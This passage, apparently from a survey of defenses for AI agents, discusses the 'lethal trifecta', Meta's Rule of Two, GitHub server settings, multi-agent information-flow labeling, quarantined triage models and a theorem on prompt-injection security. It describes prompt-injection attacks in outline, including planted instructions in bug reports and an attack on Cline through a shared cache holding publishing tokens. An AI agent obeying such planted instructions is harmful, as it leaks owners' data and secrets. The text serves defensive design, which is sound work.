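The deployer can make a claim that others are able to check if the system is missing one part of the lethal trifecta. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) requires this of any session that runs unsupervised, and counts the ability to change things alongside external communication. Several of the protections for GitHub's server amount to removing one of the three parts:

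| What the owner removes | How | What the owner gives up |
|---|---|---|
| Untrusted input | Hide text from people without push access | Most bug reports |
| Private data | Use a token limited to the public repository | Work that also needs private code |
| External communication | Make the server read-only | Pull requests by the agent |

An administrator can verify each of these from the settings, without estimating how often a model resists an attack. But if the agent keeps all three abilities and a person approves its actions, the claim again depends on that person's attention, and Meta acknowledges that a user may blindly confirm a warning.

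Some useful jobs need all three. *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (2026) describes a hypothetical security agent that must look up a new software flaw on the internet and check whether the company's AI training system uses the affected library. The agent can reach both the web and the company's valuable model weights. The paper's filter would block this combination, so the company would have to split the job between sessions or agents.

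Splitting a system among several agents creates another problem, because agents pass text to each other. *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (2026) describes one agent that reads outside email, another that reads private records, and a third that receives text from both and can make payments. Each agent can appear to follow Meta's rule when checked alone, even though the team as a whole has all three properties. The attack on Cline that Khan described used a similar gap, since the job that read strangers' issues shared a cache with the job that held the publishing tokens.

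*From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) closes this gap by labeling the files that agents share. If an agent that has read sensitive data writes a file, the system labels the file sensitive, along with any agent that reads it. The system then refuses that agent's network requests unless someone with authority has cleared the data for release. The paper's proof covers only channels the system controls, so a cache run by another company would need its own protection.

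*L3M* (2026) describes a way to keep strangers' text from reaching the main agent. To sort bug reports, a program gives each page to a separate model that has no project files or network access, and asks whether the page reports a fault in a particular component. The program accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear", and passes that word to the main agent. An instruction planted in the page can cause a wrong answer, but it can't pass on a request for the owner's salary. Because the main agent never sees what the reporter wrote, it can sort issues but can't discuss them.

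These designs allow end-to-end claims with their conditions stated. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives a computer-checked theorem of this kind, which compares a real agent with a reference agent that never makes the injected requests. The real agent is as secure as the reference if three conditions hold:

1. It behaves like the reference except for certain requests, which it makes only after reading untrusted text.
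2. The system reliably records when untrusted text has reached it.
3. A monitor blocks all of those requests without changing anything else.

A customer can ask which company is responsible for each of the theorem's conditions. For GitHub's server, the record of untrusted text would depend on the labels. An application that followed Microsoft's description of those labels would trust every issue in a private repository, and so could fail the second condition. The theorem, though still correct, would then no longer apply to that agent.
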